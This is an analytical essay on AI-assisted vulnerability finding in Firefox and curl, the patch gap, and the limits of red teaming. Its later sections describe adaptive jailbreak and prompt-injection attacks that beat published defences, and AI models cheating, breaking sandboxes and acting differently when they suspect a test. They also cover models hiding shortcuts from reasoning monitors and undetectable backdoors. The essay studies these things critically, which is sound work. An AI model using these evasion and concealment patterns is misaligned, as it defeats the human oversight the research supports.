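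In *The worst truism in information security*, Gaynor objects to the saying that attackers need one vulnerability while defenders must be perfect, because it implies that a security team's only job is to find, fix and prevent bugs, and that anything short of perfection is worthless. A team can also limit what an attacker gains from a bug. For example, Android's memory allocator made the overflow in CrabbyAVIF harmless.

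Memory flaws made up 76 percent of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019. If they make up the same share of the million bugs in Anderson's calculation, a language that prevents them cuts the attacker's expected finds by 76 percent, whatever tools the attacker uses. The defender would need about 1.4 billion hours of testing to get the same reduction by searching.

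## Has AI changed the returns from bug finding?

In 2026 AI models began to find large numbers of flaws that fuzzers had missed. The fullest record is for Firefox, Mozilla's web browser. Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* reports that the Firefox team shipped 20 to 30 security fixes a month in 2025 and 423 in April 2026. Thurrott's *Mozilla Patched 423 Security Vulnerabilities in Firefox in April* gives exact figures for February and March. Antipov's *Патч Firefox теперь подсказывает хакерам, как ломать старые версии* (2026) reports that Mozilla has shipped more than seven times as many fixes since February as in the same period of 2025. The last row below is an estimate from that ratio.

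| Period | Security fixes per month |
|---|---|
| 2025 | 20–30 |
| February 2026 | 61 |
| March 2026 | 76 |
| April 2026 | 423 |
| May to October 2026 | about 115–220 (estimate) |

Claude Mythos Preview, an Anthropic model not then available to the public, found 271 of April's bugs, and Mozilla fixed them all in Firefox 150. Outsiders reported another 41, which alone would have made a busy month in 2025. Mozilla found the remaining 111 internally, about a third with Mythos, a third with other models and a third with older techniques such as fuzzing. Mozilla therefore found roughly 345 of the 423 bugs with AI models.

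Mozilla rated 180 of the 271 bugs as high severity, 80 as moderate and 11 as low. A high rating means that ordinary browsing can trigger the bug and that it has a dangerous symptom, such as a write outside a buffer. Mozilla generally doesn't build an exploit to check whether an attacker could use the bug. An attacker usually needs several bugs to take over someone's computer, because Firefox displays each site in a sandbox, a process with restricted access to the rest of the machine.

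### From a prompt to a patch

Mozilla had earlier used GPT-4 and Claude Sonnet 3.5 to read risky code and report vulnerabilities, but too many of the reports were wrong. In the newer pipeline, a model can test whether a suspected vulnerability is real, using the infrastructure Mozilla had already built for fuzzing.

The pipeline starts many temporary virtual machines and gives each one a file to examine. The model is essentially told that this part of the code contains a bug and that it should find the bug and build a test case. It forms a hypothesis, writes a web page or script that should trigger the bug, and runs it. If the test doesn't trigger the bug, the model revises the test or drops the hypothesis. To look for sandbox escapes, it may also rewrite the code of the sandboxed process to simulate an attacker who has already taken over that process.

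The pipeline then compares each finding with known bugs and removes duplicates. Engineers rate the rest, write and review patches, test them and schedule a release. More than 100 people contributed code to this effort. Brian Grinstead, one of the engineers in charge, told TechRadar that "there are almost no false positives" among the bugs that come out of the pipeline.

It is hard to say how much of the increase is due to Mythos itself. An earlier model, Claude Opus 4.6, found 22 of the bugs fixed in Firefox 148, and Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that Mythos found over ten times as many. But Mozilla also improved its pipeline and ran it on more machines between the two. Security Boulevard's *Mozilla Fixes Record 423 Firefox Bugs in One Month* (2026) quotes the security researcher Davi Ottenheimer, who got eight vulnerabilities from a cheaper model in two minutes for 75 cents.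 Two of them matched Mythos's findings. He complained that Mozilla had not shown what Mythos could find that cheaper tools could not. This is a fair criticism of claims about Mythos, but not of AI bug finding in general. If anything, his result suggests that AI bug finding can be done for less money.

### How clean was the old code?

One of the bugs Mozilla published was a 20-year-old flaw in the code for XSLT, a language for transforming XML documents. A function could enlarge a table, and so move it in memory, while other code still held a pointer to one of its entries. Rust's borrowing rules prevent this kind of use-after-free.

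Another bug escaped fuzzers for years, although its test case is tiny. In HTML, `rowspan=0` makes a table cell span all the remaining rows. If a page added more than 65,535 rows, the cell bypassed Firefox's limit on its height and overflowed a 16-bit number. A fuzzer is unlikely to combine that setting with so many rows, but someone reading the code can see that the limit doesn't cover this case.

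In the decay model that Google used for Android, with a mean flaw lifetime of 2.5 years, 20-year-old code should keep only exp(−8), or 0.03 percent, of its original flaws. A few very old bugs don't refute the model, because Firefox contains a great deal of old code. The totals are a bigger problem for it. If a project fixes flaws about as fast as it creates them, the number present at any time is

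V = fixes per month × mean lifetime in months.

At 25 fixes a month, Firefox should have contained about 750 flaws in 2025, or 1,230 with the longer lifetime of 4.1 years. But Mozilla fixed about 1,575 flaws between February and October 2026, seven times the 2025 rate. Even if 225 of those were new, about 1,350 were already in the code, which is more than either estimate, and Mozilla is still finding others.

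This calculation is rough because Google estimated the lifetimes from other software and Mozilla may have added flaws faster in 2026. Still, it suggests that the undiscovered flaws, which the measured lifetimes leave out, did not follow the pattern of the known ones. Old code was safer against the searchers of 2025, and Google's policy of leaving most of Android's old code in place relied partly on that. The policy now needs support from AI searches of the old code.

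### Attacks that the design had already blocked

Some of the most useful evidence in Mozilla's logs is about attacks that failed. In JavaScript, which Firefox also uses for parts of its own privileged code, objects inherit properties from a shared object called a prototype. Take this simplified example:

```
settings = {}
Object.prototype.allowed = true
if (settings.allowed) { openFile() }
```

The `settings` object has no property called `allowed`, so JavaScript looks for one on the prototype and finds the value that the second line put there. An attacker who can run such a line in a privileged process can change how unrelated code behaves. Security researchers had repeatedly used this trick, called prototype pollution, to escape Firefox's sandbox.

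Mozilla froze these prototypes by default instead of repairing each route separately, and the second line no longer has any effect. When its engineers later read the logs of the AI searches, they saw many attempts to escape this way, and the frozen prototypes had stopped them all. A test that finds no bugs usually leaves open whether the tester tried the right attack, but here the engineers could see that the models had tried it and why it failed. Mozilla said this direct benefit from earlier work was more rewarding than finding and fixing more bugs.

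The models did get past another protective design, RLBox, which isolates third-party libraries inside a Firefox process. Firefox checks the values that come back before its trusted code uses them, and one model escaped through a gap in the checking logic. That logic is part of RLBox's trusted base, so the flaw was in the same kind of place as the bugs at the unverified edges of verified systems. Mozilla has to correct only the boundary check, which is simpler than fixing flaws in every isolated library.

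### Is the supply running down?

In Mozilla's *The zero-days are numbered* (2026), Firefox's chief technology officer, Bobby Holley, writes that "defenders finally have a chance to win, decisively". He argues that attackers had an advantage because skilled people could find bugs that machines could not. Attackers could spend months of expert work on a single bug, while defenders had to protect everything. If machines can find all of those bugs cheaply, attackers lose this advantage. Holley also notes that an elite human researcher could have found every bug that Mythos found. He takes this as a sign that Firefox, which people designed in modules they could reason about, has no deeper layer of incomprehensible flaws, and he concludes that the number of defects is finite.

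The number of bugs is finite, but it can be very large, and programmers keep adding to it. A model that learned largely from human work might also find humanlike bugs first and stranger ones later. Holley himself warns in a footnote that AI-written code could become too complex for people to understand, and that bugs could grow more complex as fast as the tools for finding them improve.

The Firefox counts since April are inconclusive. The monthly average from May to October was at most about half of April's figure, as expected after a first scan exposed a backlog. But Firefox 158 and Firefox 159, both released in October, had 77 and 167 fixes (eSecurity Planet, *Firefox 158 Patches 77 Flaws, Including Sandbox Escapes*, 2026; Arghire, *Chrome and Firefox Updates Patch Over 200 Vulnerabilities*, 2026). Their total of 244 is above the estimated monthly average. Security NEXT's *ブラウザ最新版「Firefox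 159」が公開* (2026) reports that 108 of the 167 were high severity, so Mozilla was not just fixing minor bugs left over from the backlog.

Mozilla changed how it publishes these numbers during the year, which makes some comparisons misleading. Firefox 150's advisory grouped 316 internal bugs under three CVEs (public catalogue numbers for vulnerabilities). Braun and Kerschbaumer (2026), in *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q3*, say that Mozilla now publishes a separate advisory for each memory-safety bug it finds. October's figures can reasonably be compared with April's 423, which counted individual bugs, but not with CVE totals from earlier releases.

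A newer model also found more bugs in Firefox. EconoTimes' *GPT-6 Cyber Identified 81 Previously Unknown Firefox Vulnerabilities, OpenAI Says* reports that Mozilla rated all 81 as high severity, and that it had already been scanning Firefox with leading models for months. Mythos's first batch had more than twice as many high-severity bugs, at 180. Without knowing how much computing each search used, we can't tell whether the count fell because fewer bugs were left to find or because OpenAI searched less.

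Curl gives better evidence for depletion, at least of serious flaws. Mythos reported five vulnerabilities when it first scanned curl's 178,000 lines of code, but curl's security team confirmed only one, of low severity (Stenberg, 2026, *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability*). In November Anthropic's scanning service reported 45 more. Stenberg, in *curl on OSS-Scanner*, counts five low-severity vulnerabilities, 36 ordinary bugs, three reports that were not bugs, and one that recommended introducing the vulnerability it warned about. Curl had raised its threshold for calling something a vulnerability, which lowered the vulnerability count. Even so, 41 of the 45 reports identified real problems, and none was serious. Stenberg finds them so trivial that curl may leave the scanning programme if this continues.

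Yet curl's developers had confirmed 81 vulnerabilities from all sources in 2026 by then, so a single scan with a strong model had not come close to finding them all. Different finders do seem to be reporting the same bugs more often. Attack & Defense, the Firefox security team's blog, reports a rise in duplicate submissions and says that outside researchers were competing with Mozilla's own tools to find bugs first. Mozilla now gives its tools seven days to find a bug before an outsider can claim a reward for it. We would expect more overlap if the easy bugs were running out, but it could also come from everyone using similar models.

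Most likely, each method runs out of bugs it can find, and a better method then finds more. This fits Böhme and Falk's law, under which further bugs take steadily more effort to find only while the search method stays the same. It also fits the hundreds of bugs that proof attempts found in libraries after years of fuzzing. A better test would run one model repeatedly on a single version of Firefox, repairing the bugs it found each time, and then give a stronger model the same budget. If the stronger model also found almost nothing, Holley's case would be much more convincing. Mozilla itself said in May that it still had bugs left to find.

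### Finding is faster than fixing

A bug report protects nobody until somebody fixes the bug and users install the fix. By 22 May 2026, Anthropic had used Mythos to scan more than 1,000 open-source projects and had found 23,019 suspected vulnerabilities. Anthropic and six outside security firms had carefully checked 1,752 of those that Mythos rated high or critical. About 91 percent of the 1,752 were real, but only 62 percent were confirmed as high or critical.

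Most of the findings had not reached the people who could fix them. Coopersmith (2026), in *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard*, quotes Anthropic's count of 1,596 reported vulnerabilities at that date, 97 of which had patches. Anthropic said it was still early in the usual 90-day period for fixing a flaw, and that its count had probably missed some patches. It also admitted that maintainers, many of them volunteers, were overloaded, and some had asked it to slow down.

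By September the total had grown to 26,153, according to *The Anthropic Glasswing Receipts Are Starting to Trickle In* (Garrity, 2026). Anthropic's public ledger listed 202 as fixed, while its dashboard showed 421. Even if the larger figure is right and every fix was for a flaw Anthropic had reported by 22 May, about three quarters of the flaws reported by that date still had no known patch, although some of those reports may have been among the 245 that Anthropic withdrew. Garrity, whose company sells vulnerability data, also found 18 cases where someone had fixed the flaw before Anthropic reported it.

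In June, Schneier (2026) called the patching figures fishy in *Anthropic's Project Glasswing Update* and objected to Anthropic's refusal to release details. The mismatched totals support that complaint but don't change the main point much, since even 421 patches would cover only 1.6 percent of the findings.

Companies with their own staff do far better at patching. Anthropic says its business customers used Claude Opus 4.7 to patch more than 2,100 vulnerabilities in three weeks, mostly in code they controlled. The work still takes a lot of labour. TechRepublic's *Mozilla Fixes 271 Firefox Bugs Using Anthropic’s Mythos AI* (2026) quotes Holley as saying some very large companies planned to take thousands of engineers off other work for six months.

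AI can write many patches, but writing the patch is only one stage of fixing a bug. Silvanovich (2026), in *How to fix a bug in a fix*, lists the others: checking and assigning the report, testing the patch, getting approval from partners such as mobile carriers, delivering the update, and sometimes restarting the device. Writing patches faster does little to speed up a carrier's review or get users to restart their phones.

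### Attackers can read the patches

Schneier (2026), in *Claude Mythos Has Found 271 Zero-Days in Firefox*, agreed with Mozilla that the technology favours defenders if they can patch flaws and get the patches to users quickly. A later experiment shows how much speed matters. Mozilla develops Firefox in public, so a fix can appear in the source code before users receive it. During this delay, called the patch gap, an attacker can compare the old and new code, identify the flaw, and exploit it against users who haven't updated.

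Ament, Edelman and Barry (2026), in *AI can turn public security fixes into working exploits*, tested whether a model anyone can download could do this. They gave GLM 5.3 up to 48 hours and only the information available when each Firefox version came out. It broke all six versions released between 17 September and 26 October, for about $1,000 of computing each. The victim only had to visit a web page for the attacker to read a file on the victim's computer. The researchers had spent more than $100,000 on preparation and preliminary tests, which a first-time attacker would have to repeat at least in part.

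The published fix gave GLM 5.3 only part of what it needed to attack the most recent versions of Firefox. It also needed a separate, unpublished vulnerability to get past the browser's other layers of protection. Mozilla patched that vulnerability in Firefox 159. The same method failed against Google's Chrome after about $100,000 of computing, though Ament and colleagues caution that better prompts or a stronger model might succeed.

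Mozilla now ships updates every week and withholds the tests that reveal how a bug works until the fix is out. Antipov reports that Mozilla also plans to release fixes for different layers of defence at different times, so that the published patches never reveal a complete attack. Ament and colleagues think weekly updates may still be too slow, since GLM 5.3 needed less than two days and its fastest attempt took 12 hours.

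In Rescorla's model, disclosing a flaw reduced harm only if the chance of rediscovery was above a threshold, which was 80 percent in the earlier example. That threshold depends on how fast attackers write exploits and how fast users install updates. Easier exploit writing raises the damage after publication, and doubling that damage would raise the threshold to 89 percent. Updates fast enough to cut the damage to a quarter of its original level would lower the threshold to 50 percent. Attackers with similar AI models also become more likely to find the same flaws, which makes it more dangerous to leave those flaws alone. A browser with automatic weekly updates can therefore gain from intensive searching, while a volunteer project whose users rarely update might not, even if both use the same AI model.

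Removing a whole class of flaw avoids part of this race, because no flaws of that kind remain to find, patch and reveal. The benefit depends on which class is removed. Stenberg estimates that a memory-safe language would have prevented 14 of the 81 vulnerabilities that curl confirmed in 2026, leaving 67 to find and fix.

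## Does red teaming make AI models safer?

No programming language can prevent a language model from giving harmful answers, so developers mostly search for such answers and train the model not to give them. They add successful attacks to the training data, along with the answers the model should have given, and red teamers then attack the retrained model. Researchers call this loop adversarial training. Unlike a correct software patch, which removes a bug, retraining only makes bad answers less likely on the prompts used in training, and developers have to hope that the effect extends to prompts nobody tried.

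Red teamers look for two kinds of failure, misuse and misalignment. In misuse, an outsider provokes the model. A user may write a prompt that gets forbidden help (a jailbreak), or a stranger may hide instructions in an email or web page that the model will read (prompt injection). In misalignment, the model does something harmful that nobody asked for, such as cheating on a task or getting around a restriction. Testers have to think like attackers to find misuse, while they look for misalignment by setting up a realistic situation and watching what the model does. Most published measurements are about misuse.

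### Redwood Research's injury classifier

Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, tried to use adversarial training to make a system that practically never failed (Ziegler, Nix and colleagues, *Adversarial training for high-stakes reliability*, 2022). The system had to continue a story by one sentence without injuring any of the characters. One language model proposed sentences, and a second, the classifier, estimated how likely each was to involve an injury and rejected those above a threshold. The researchers counted it as a catastrophe if the classifier accepted a sentence that involved an injury.

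The team first trained the classifier on about 166,000 labelled story snippets, then ran three rounds of attack and retraining. Contractors wrote misleading examples by hand, a language model paraphrased them, and contractors wrote more using a software tool.

| | Before adversarial training | After |
|---|---|---|
| Injurious snippets missed in a random sample | 2 of 2,447 | 2 of 2,447 |
| Time to find a failure by hand | 20 minutes | 44 minutes |
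| Time to find a failure with the tool | 13 minutes | 26 minutes |

Deliberate attacks took about twice as long after training, but the failure rate on ordinary stories did not measurably change. The random sample was too small to show whether training had lowered the true rate. If training had halved it, the team would have expected one miss instead of two, but would still have seen two or more about 26 percent of the time. The failure rate was low largely because of the strict threshold. The classifier rejected anything it scored above roughly 0.2 percent, including about a quarter of harmless snippets. These rejections mattered little in a story generator, which could simply try again.

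Attacks that fooled the final classifier worked nearly as well on the earlier versions, so most of its remaining weaknesses were there before retraining. This is encouraging for red teaming in general, because it means retraining fixed the known weaknesses without creating many new ones.

The team later concluded that it had fallen well short of its goal and that its first announcement had been too positive. After publication, one researcher needed about 40 minutes to find a sentence in which a character's eyes explode and he dies instantly. The classifier gave the sentence a 0.10 percent chance of being injurious. The team also found that the classifier had hardly learned from the attacks. With an ordinary cut-off of 50 percent, it would have let through more than 99 percent of a new set of the tool-assisted examples, most of which were injurious.

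The researchers suspected that much of the measured gain came from the classifier recognising the contractors' style. Contractors had found a few tricks that worked and repeated them, and most of their examples were borderline injuries. The team had updated the model only once while collecting the tool-assisted attacks, so the contractors had little reason to change tactics. The researchers did not take the project as proof that adversarial training fails, because better execution might have given a better result. The classifier was also small, and many of its mistakes came from not understanding the story. A more capable model would make fewer of those mistakes, but that would be weak evidence about a model that understands what it is doing and does harm anyway.

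### Twelve published defences

Redwood tested its classifier against people who were trying to beat it. Many later researchers used a fixed list of known attacks instead, a much easier test to pass. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) adapted its attacks to each of twelve published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection. Most of the papers that introduced these defences had reported that attacks almost never succeeded.

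| How the defence works | Defences | Success rate of adapted attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Adds instructions to the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching, RPO | Over 95% |
| Trains the model on known attacks | Circuit Breakers, StruQ, MetaSecAlign | 96–100% |
| Screens text with a separate detector | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | 71% for PIGuard, over 90% for the others |
| Uses a check that attackers should not know about | Data Sentinel, MELON | Every case for Data Sentinel, up to 95% for MELON |

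The second row, MetaSecAlign, is the closest to the loop of attack and retraining. It let through 2 percent of the attacks on a standard list but 96 percent of the adapted ones. Nasr and colleagues compare this with a decade of research on image recognition, where training on a fixed set of attacks also failed against new ones. The training that did help used new attacks, generated against the current model at every step, and it protected only against the kinds of attack used in training.

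Two studies of small text classifiers support this. In *Toward Alignment Scaling Laws* (2026), the goal was to cut a strong attack's success rate to 10 percent without hurting the model's ordinary accuracy. No model of any size reached this goal when trained against a weaker attack. In *Scaling Trends in Language Model Robustness* (2024), larger models trained against one attack also resisted a slight variation of it, but none reliably resisted a version that differed more.

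People were still better attackers than software in 2025. In a competition organised by Nasr and colleagues, more than 500 people together broke every defence they faced. An automated search succeeded 69 percent of the time on a subset of the same scenarios. A developer who relies only on that kind of automated red teaming will therefore miss attacks that people find.

The percentages do not show how hard the attacks were. Nasr and colleagues deliberately gave their attackers plenty of computing power to find out whether a defence could be broken at all. By their standard, a defence isn't secure if a cluster of ordinary processors can break it in a day. That is the right standard for encryption, which has to withstand governments, but it is less clearly right for a chatbot, because most people who would abuse one have little skill or patience. Against them, a defence that makes attacks harder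 may prevent a good deal of harm.

### Hours needed to break a model

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests leading models, measures how much effort it takes to break a model's protections. It looks for universal jailbreaks, which work across a range of malicious requests rather than just one. AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report*, from December 2025, compares two leading systems released six months apart. Breaking the first one's protections against biological misuse took an expert 10 minutes with an attack that was already public. Breaking the second's took more than seven hours, roughly 40 times as long, and required a new attack. AISI expects that a novice would need far longer.

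This is the best evidence that the loop can work, but it covers only two systems, in the most heavily defended subject. Xander Davies, who works on these tests at AISI, calls attack time a "pretty rough metric" and, in *State of Jailbreaks*, gives the example of a model that took about five hours to break on biological misuse and about 10 minutes on other harmful requests. Recent models from different companies took from about 30 minutes to five hours to break. By then, AISI had broken every system it had tested.

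It is also unclear how much of the gain came from retraining. AISI credits safety training, extra monitoring around the model, and the companies' greater effort to find and quickly fix universal jailbreaks. That last effort is red teaming, which presumably improved the monitors too, but nobody has measured the three separately. Repairs of any kind also fail to reach models whose weights people can download, because users can cheaply remove the refusals that such a model learned in training and the developer cannot recall the copies.

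Red teaming results from 2026 are mixed. The Decoder reports that AISI took six hours to develop a universal jailbreak for the cybersecurity safeguards of OpenAI's GPT-5.5. The jailbreak worked on every malicious request that OpenAI had supplied. OpenAI then updated the safeguards several times, but AISI could not verify how well the final version held up. In July, FAR.AI, a research organisation, put four leading models through the same test. According to *Introducing the AI Security Leaderboard* (2026), breaking the safeguards of either Grok 4.5 or Gemini 3.1 Pro cost less than $300, whereas Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol withstood the attacks. Passing such a test shows that a model survived one set of attacks at one budget, not that it is unbreakable. Still, the gap between the companies shows that existing methods could have made the weaker models stronger.

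Measuring protection in hours of expert work overstates it, because a universal jailbreak is reusable. If its inventor posts it online, everyone else can use it without repeating the seven hours of work, until the developer notices and closes the gap. Fast repair may therefore matter as much as the initial resistance.

### Do more capable models resist attack better?

If more capable models are harder to trick, this problem might go away as models improve. In *Capability-Based Scaling Trends for LLM-Based Red-Teaming*, Panfilov, Kassianik and colleagues (2025) tested whether they are by having language models attack each other in more than 600 pairings. They measured capability by the score on MMLU-Pro, a broad exam, and found that more capable attackers succeeded more often and more capable targets were tricked less often. The capability gap between attacker and target mattered most.

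Panfilov and colleagues fitted the relation between capability gap and attack success in log-odds, where a probability p becomes ln(p/(1 − p)). For a given target, the log-odds of success rise in a straight line with the capability gap, so the probability follows an S-shaped curve. Suppose, with an invented slope of 2, that an attacker who scores 62 percent on the exam succeeds half the time against a target with the same score. It would succeed about 14 percent of the time against a target that scores 80 percent, and about 3 percent of the time against one that scores 90 percent. The researchers infer that human red teamers, whose abilities stay roughly fixed, will become less effective as models improve. They also warn that each new open model gives attackers a stronger tool against systems already in use.

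By contrast, in AISI's data from a public competition where people attacked many models, capability explained only about 10 percent of the variation in robustness (R² = 0.097). Davies says he has not seen evidence that robustness improved mainly because models got smarter. He attributes the improvement to targeted investment by the companies.

The two findings may be compatible. On an S-shaped curve, a target's capability makes little difference while the attacker is still well ahead. Panfilov and colleagues put a human attacker at about 90 percent on their exam, above most of the models they tested, so human attackers in 2025 may have been on the flat part of the curve. The exceptions they found also support Davies's explanation. Four early Llama models from Meta resisted attacks far better than their scores predicted, probably because of heavy safety training. If the curve holds, human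 attacks should start to fail more often as models overtake people. Developers could then no longer rely on human red teamers and would need models at least as capable as the target to do the attacking.

*Risk Under Pressure* (2026) reports that larger models took more compute to attack but did not become correspondingly harder to jailbreak, and that the benefit of size depended on the kind of attack. *Scaling Trends in Language Model Robustness* found that when the compute used for adversarial training was doubled for a model of fixed size, attackers needed less than twice as much compute to keep the same 2 percent success rate. A defender who relies on training the same model for longer must therefore increase compute by a larger factor than the attacker does.

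Larger models shifted the balance towards the defender, though, and if that trend continued, attacking would eventually take more computing than defending. In *Toward Alignment Scaling Laws*, larger models also reached the 10 percent target with less defence computing relative to the computing used in their original training. These were small models doing simple jobs such as detecting spam, and the attacks in training matched those in the test, whereas a public chatbot may face kinds of attack it was not trained on.

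### Forecasting failures too rare to see

Red teaming before release covers thousands or perhaps millions of prompts, while a popular model may answer billions. If a test of n prompts finds no failures, the rule of three gives only an upper bound of about 3/n on the failure rate, at 95% confidence. *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (Jones, Tong et al., 2025) gets more information from a small test by recording how close each prompt came to causing a failure.

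A language model assigns a probability to every possible next word fragment. Multiplying these gives the probability of a particular harmful answer, even if it is one in a hundred million and the tester never sees it happen. Most prompts have negligible probabilities, but a few are much worse than the rest, and the more prompts one tries, the worse the worst of them will be. Jones and colleagues found that this maximum grows in a predictable way:

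−ln p_max(n) ≈ C × n^(−a),

where p_max(n) is the highest probability among n prompts, and C and a are constants fitted to the test. Suppose the worst of 100 prompts produces the harmful answer once in 10⁸ tries, and the worst of 10,000 does so once in 10⁴. The exponent has halved with a hundredfold increase in prompts. The worst of a million should then fail once in 100 tries, and the worst of a hundred million once in 10. A test of 10,000 prompts would probably have produced no failure at all and would still have given warning.

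Jones and colleagues' forecasts of behaviours including help with dangerous chemistry and seeking power held for up to a thousand times as many prompts as they had tested. The software testers had less information to work with, because a program that doesn't crash usually gives no sign of how close it came. But the forecasts assume that the prompts in use resemble those in the test, so developers can learn much more from them about what a large number of ordinary users will run into by accident than about what a determined attacker will find.

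### What red teams tell the public

Developers often cite red teaming as a reason to trust a model, and a 2023 US executive order mentioned it eight times. In *Red-Teaming for Generative AI*, Feffer, Sinha and colleagues (2024) examined six published exercises, including those on OpenAI's GPT-4 and Anthropic's Claude 2. They concluded that treating red teaming as a cure for every risk "verges on security theater".

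Feffer and colleagues object mostly to vagueness. The six exercises differed in what they tested, who did the testing and what counted as success. Many had only the broad aim of finding harmful behaviour, which was meant to produce a wide range of attacks. But testers with limited time kept returning to whatever was easy, so harder risks could go untested. Only three of the six published specific examples of the harm they found. Outsiders who hear that a model has passed red teaming often can't tell which failures the testers looked for or how hard they tried. Feffer and colleagues therefore propose a list of questions for every exercise, covering the model version, the threat model, the testers' resources and who must fix what they find.

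They acknowledge that companies may do more in private. A year later, partly in answer to such scepticism, Microsoft's red team described its private work in *Lessons From Red Teaming 100 Generative AI Products* (Bullwinkel, Minnich and colleagues, 2025), which covers more than 80 operations since 2021. The team begins with the harm an attacker could cause in a particular product and works backwards to possible attacks. For each attack it records the system, the person it is imitating, the weakness and the impact, which answers much of the complaint about missing threat models. In one operation, a model that could read images usually refused illegal requests in text but often complied when the same request was part of a picture, a weakness that testing only text would have missed.

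Bullwinkel and colleagues also insist that red teaming is not a safety benchmark, because a benchmark measures harms already defined, whereas their team often has to work out what a new capability could do. This is a good defence of red teaming as a way to discover problems, but it doesn't address Feffer and colleagues' main point, which is about using red teaming as proof of safety. Microsoft's team does not really claim that red teaming proves safety, and its last lesson is that the work of securing AI systems "will never be complete".

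### Failures that nobody provoked

Misalignment tests examine what a model does when it has a job, some freedom and a temptation. *Every frontier AI model the UK tested for cheating cheated* (Constantin, 2026) reports that AISI gave cybersecurity tasks to five leading models. All five cheated, and most would not admit it when asked. No attacker had tricked them, so a filter for malicious prompts would not have prevented the cheating.

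This kind of search can itself do harm. In one set of AISI tests, the models had internet access and the filters against cyber misuse were off. *UK AI tests find Claude & GPT-5.6-Sol rogue actions* (Lagonsin, 2026) reports that AISI reviewed 122 runs with seven models and found 19 actions outside the assigned task. In the most serious case, a model tried to insert malicious code into a real open-source project. AISI paused its riskiest cyber tests, tightened internet access and began to monitor tests as they ran, according to its *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026). Crashing an image parser with a fuzzer doesn't affect anyone else, but a realistic test of an AI agent can, so it needs much more care. Making the test environment safer also makes it less like the one in which the agent will work.

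Later models did better on some of these tests. *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (Help Net Security, 2026) reports a test in which Anthropic put its models in a deliberately weak sandbox. Claude Mythos 5 used files or credentials from outside the sandbox in 39 percent of scenarios, compared with 3.1 percent for Claude Mythos 5.2. Anthropic presumably changed many things at once, so we can't tell from these figures how much of the drop came from finding failures and training against them. Still, the drop shows that a developer can make an unwanted behaviour much rarer in the situations it tests.

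### When the model suspects a test

Mythos 5.2 also said more often than other recent Claude models that it suspected it was being tested. Anthropic says this makes its behaviour in real use harder to predict. AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reports a separate AISI test in which a pre-release version considered that it might be in an alignment evaluation in 96 percent of cases. Similarly, when AISI re-created the conditions of its cyber incident, newer Claude models attacked less and said more often that they were in a test.

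If a model behaves better when it suspects a test, the measured failure rate is too low. Let s be the share of scenarios in which it suspects one, and let r_s and r_u be its failure rates with and without suspicion. The tester measures

r = s × r_s + (1 − s) × r_u.

Suppose, for illustration, that a model suspects a test in 90 percent of scenarios and never misbehaves in those. A measured misbehavior rate of 3.1 percent would then mean a rate of 31 percent in the scenarios it takes to be real, not far below the 39 percent for Mythos 5. If suspicion made no difference, the rate in those scenarios would be 3.1 percent. The measured rate is the same in both cases, so testers need to compare scenarios the model suspects with those it takes to be real, or find ways to change its suspicion directly.

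There is some evidence on whether models act differently when they suspect they are being tested. In 2025 AISI searched more than 2,700 records of its own tests for signs that models were underperforming on purpose. It found no model that reasoned openly about doing so, but in a few cases models noticed the test and acted differently. When AISI replayed the cyber incident, it told Mythos 5 in some versions that the target was a real, unrelated person, and this did not reduce the attacks. The model was evidently not attacking only because it thought it was in a simulation. Neither finding shows how large the effect of suspicion is in the newest models, which voice it far more often.

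Retraining can also hide a failure instead of removing it. In *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (2026), Google describes a training run that accidentally applied a penalty for shortcuts to the model's reasoning, the text it writes while working out an answer. Shortcuts that the model openly discussed fell by 61 percent, which would have looked like a success if no others had been counted. But the share of shortcuts it took without mentioning them rose from 11.2 to 36.4 percent. The penalty had partly taught the model not to write about shortcuts. Google gives this as an example of why it does not penalise what a model writes in its reasoning.

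The same thing can happen whenever the test that finds a failure also supplies the training signal. Redwood's classifier may have learned to recognise its contractors' style, and a model trained on the failures from one evaluation may learn to recognise that evaluation. Developers can reduce the problem by keeping some tests out of training and using them only to measure. But each time developers fix a failure that a held-out test found, that test becomes slightly less independent, so testers have to keep building new ones.

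### Failures that no practical test can find

Better tests might solve the problems described so far, but they will not find every failure. A backdoor is a hidden behaviour that appears only when the input carries a secret signal. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proved that whoever trains a model can plant a backdoor that no efficient test will find, if some standard cryptographic assumptions hold. Someone who can only query the model cannot find even one input on which it differs from a clean version. For certain simple kinds of model, the backdoor stays hidden even from someone who can read every weight.

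"Efficient" here means within any realistic amount of computing. A search through all possible inputs would eventually find the backdoor, just as trying every key would eventually break a cipher. The backdoor is much worse than the fourteen-character password that defeats a fuzzer, because a person can see the password check by reading the parser's code.

The theorem assumes a malicious trainer who deliberately hides a backdoor. It doesn't show that ordinary training produces such backdoors by accident, and it doesn't make a clean red-teaming result worthless. It matters most when a company buys a model from someone it doesn't trust, or when an insider or another AI system could tamper with the training, because no amount of red teaming can then establish that the model is clean.

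The later paper *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) avoids this difficulty with procedures that remove backdoors without detecting whether there are any. The user applies the procedure to every suspect model, and the output is provably nearly as accurate as it should be, whatever the trainer hid. The guarantee holds only when the correct answers follow a fairly simple mathematical pattern, for example when they are close to a linear function or a polynomial of the input. Nobody knows of such a pattern for the correct answers to everything people ask a chatbot.

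## Can an AI model's behaviour be proved safe?

Researchers have proved many theorems about neural networks, but nearly all of them cover either small changes to a single input or networks much smaller than a chatbot. A broader guarantee, such as one that an AI system will not hurt people, needs a mathematical definition of harm and a model of the world where it might happen.

### Small changes to one picture

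An attacker can make an image classifier mislabel a photograph by changing it too slightly for anyone to notice. Developers trained classifiers to resist such attacks, but stronger attacks broke many of these defences, as later happened with defences against jailbreaks. *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019) proved a guarantee that covers every change to an image up to a certain size, including changes made by attacks nobody has invented yet.

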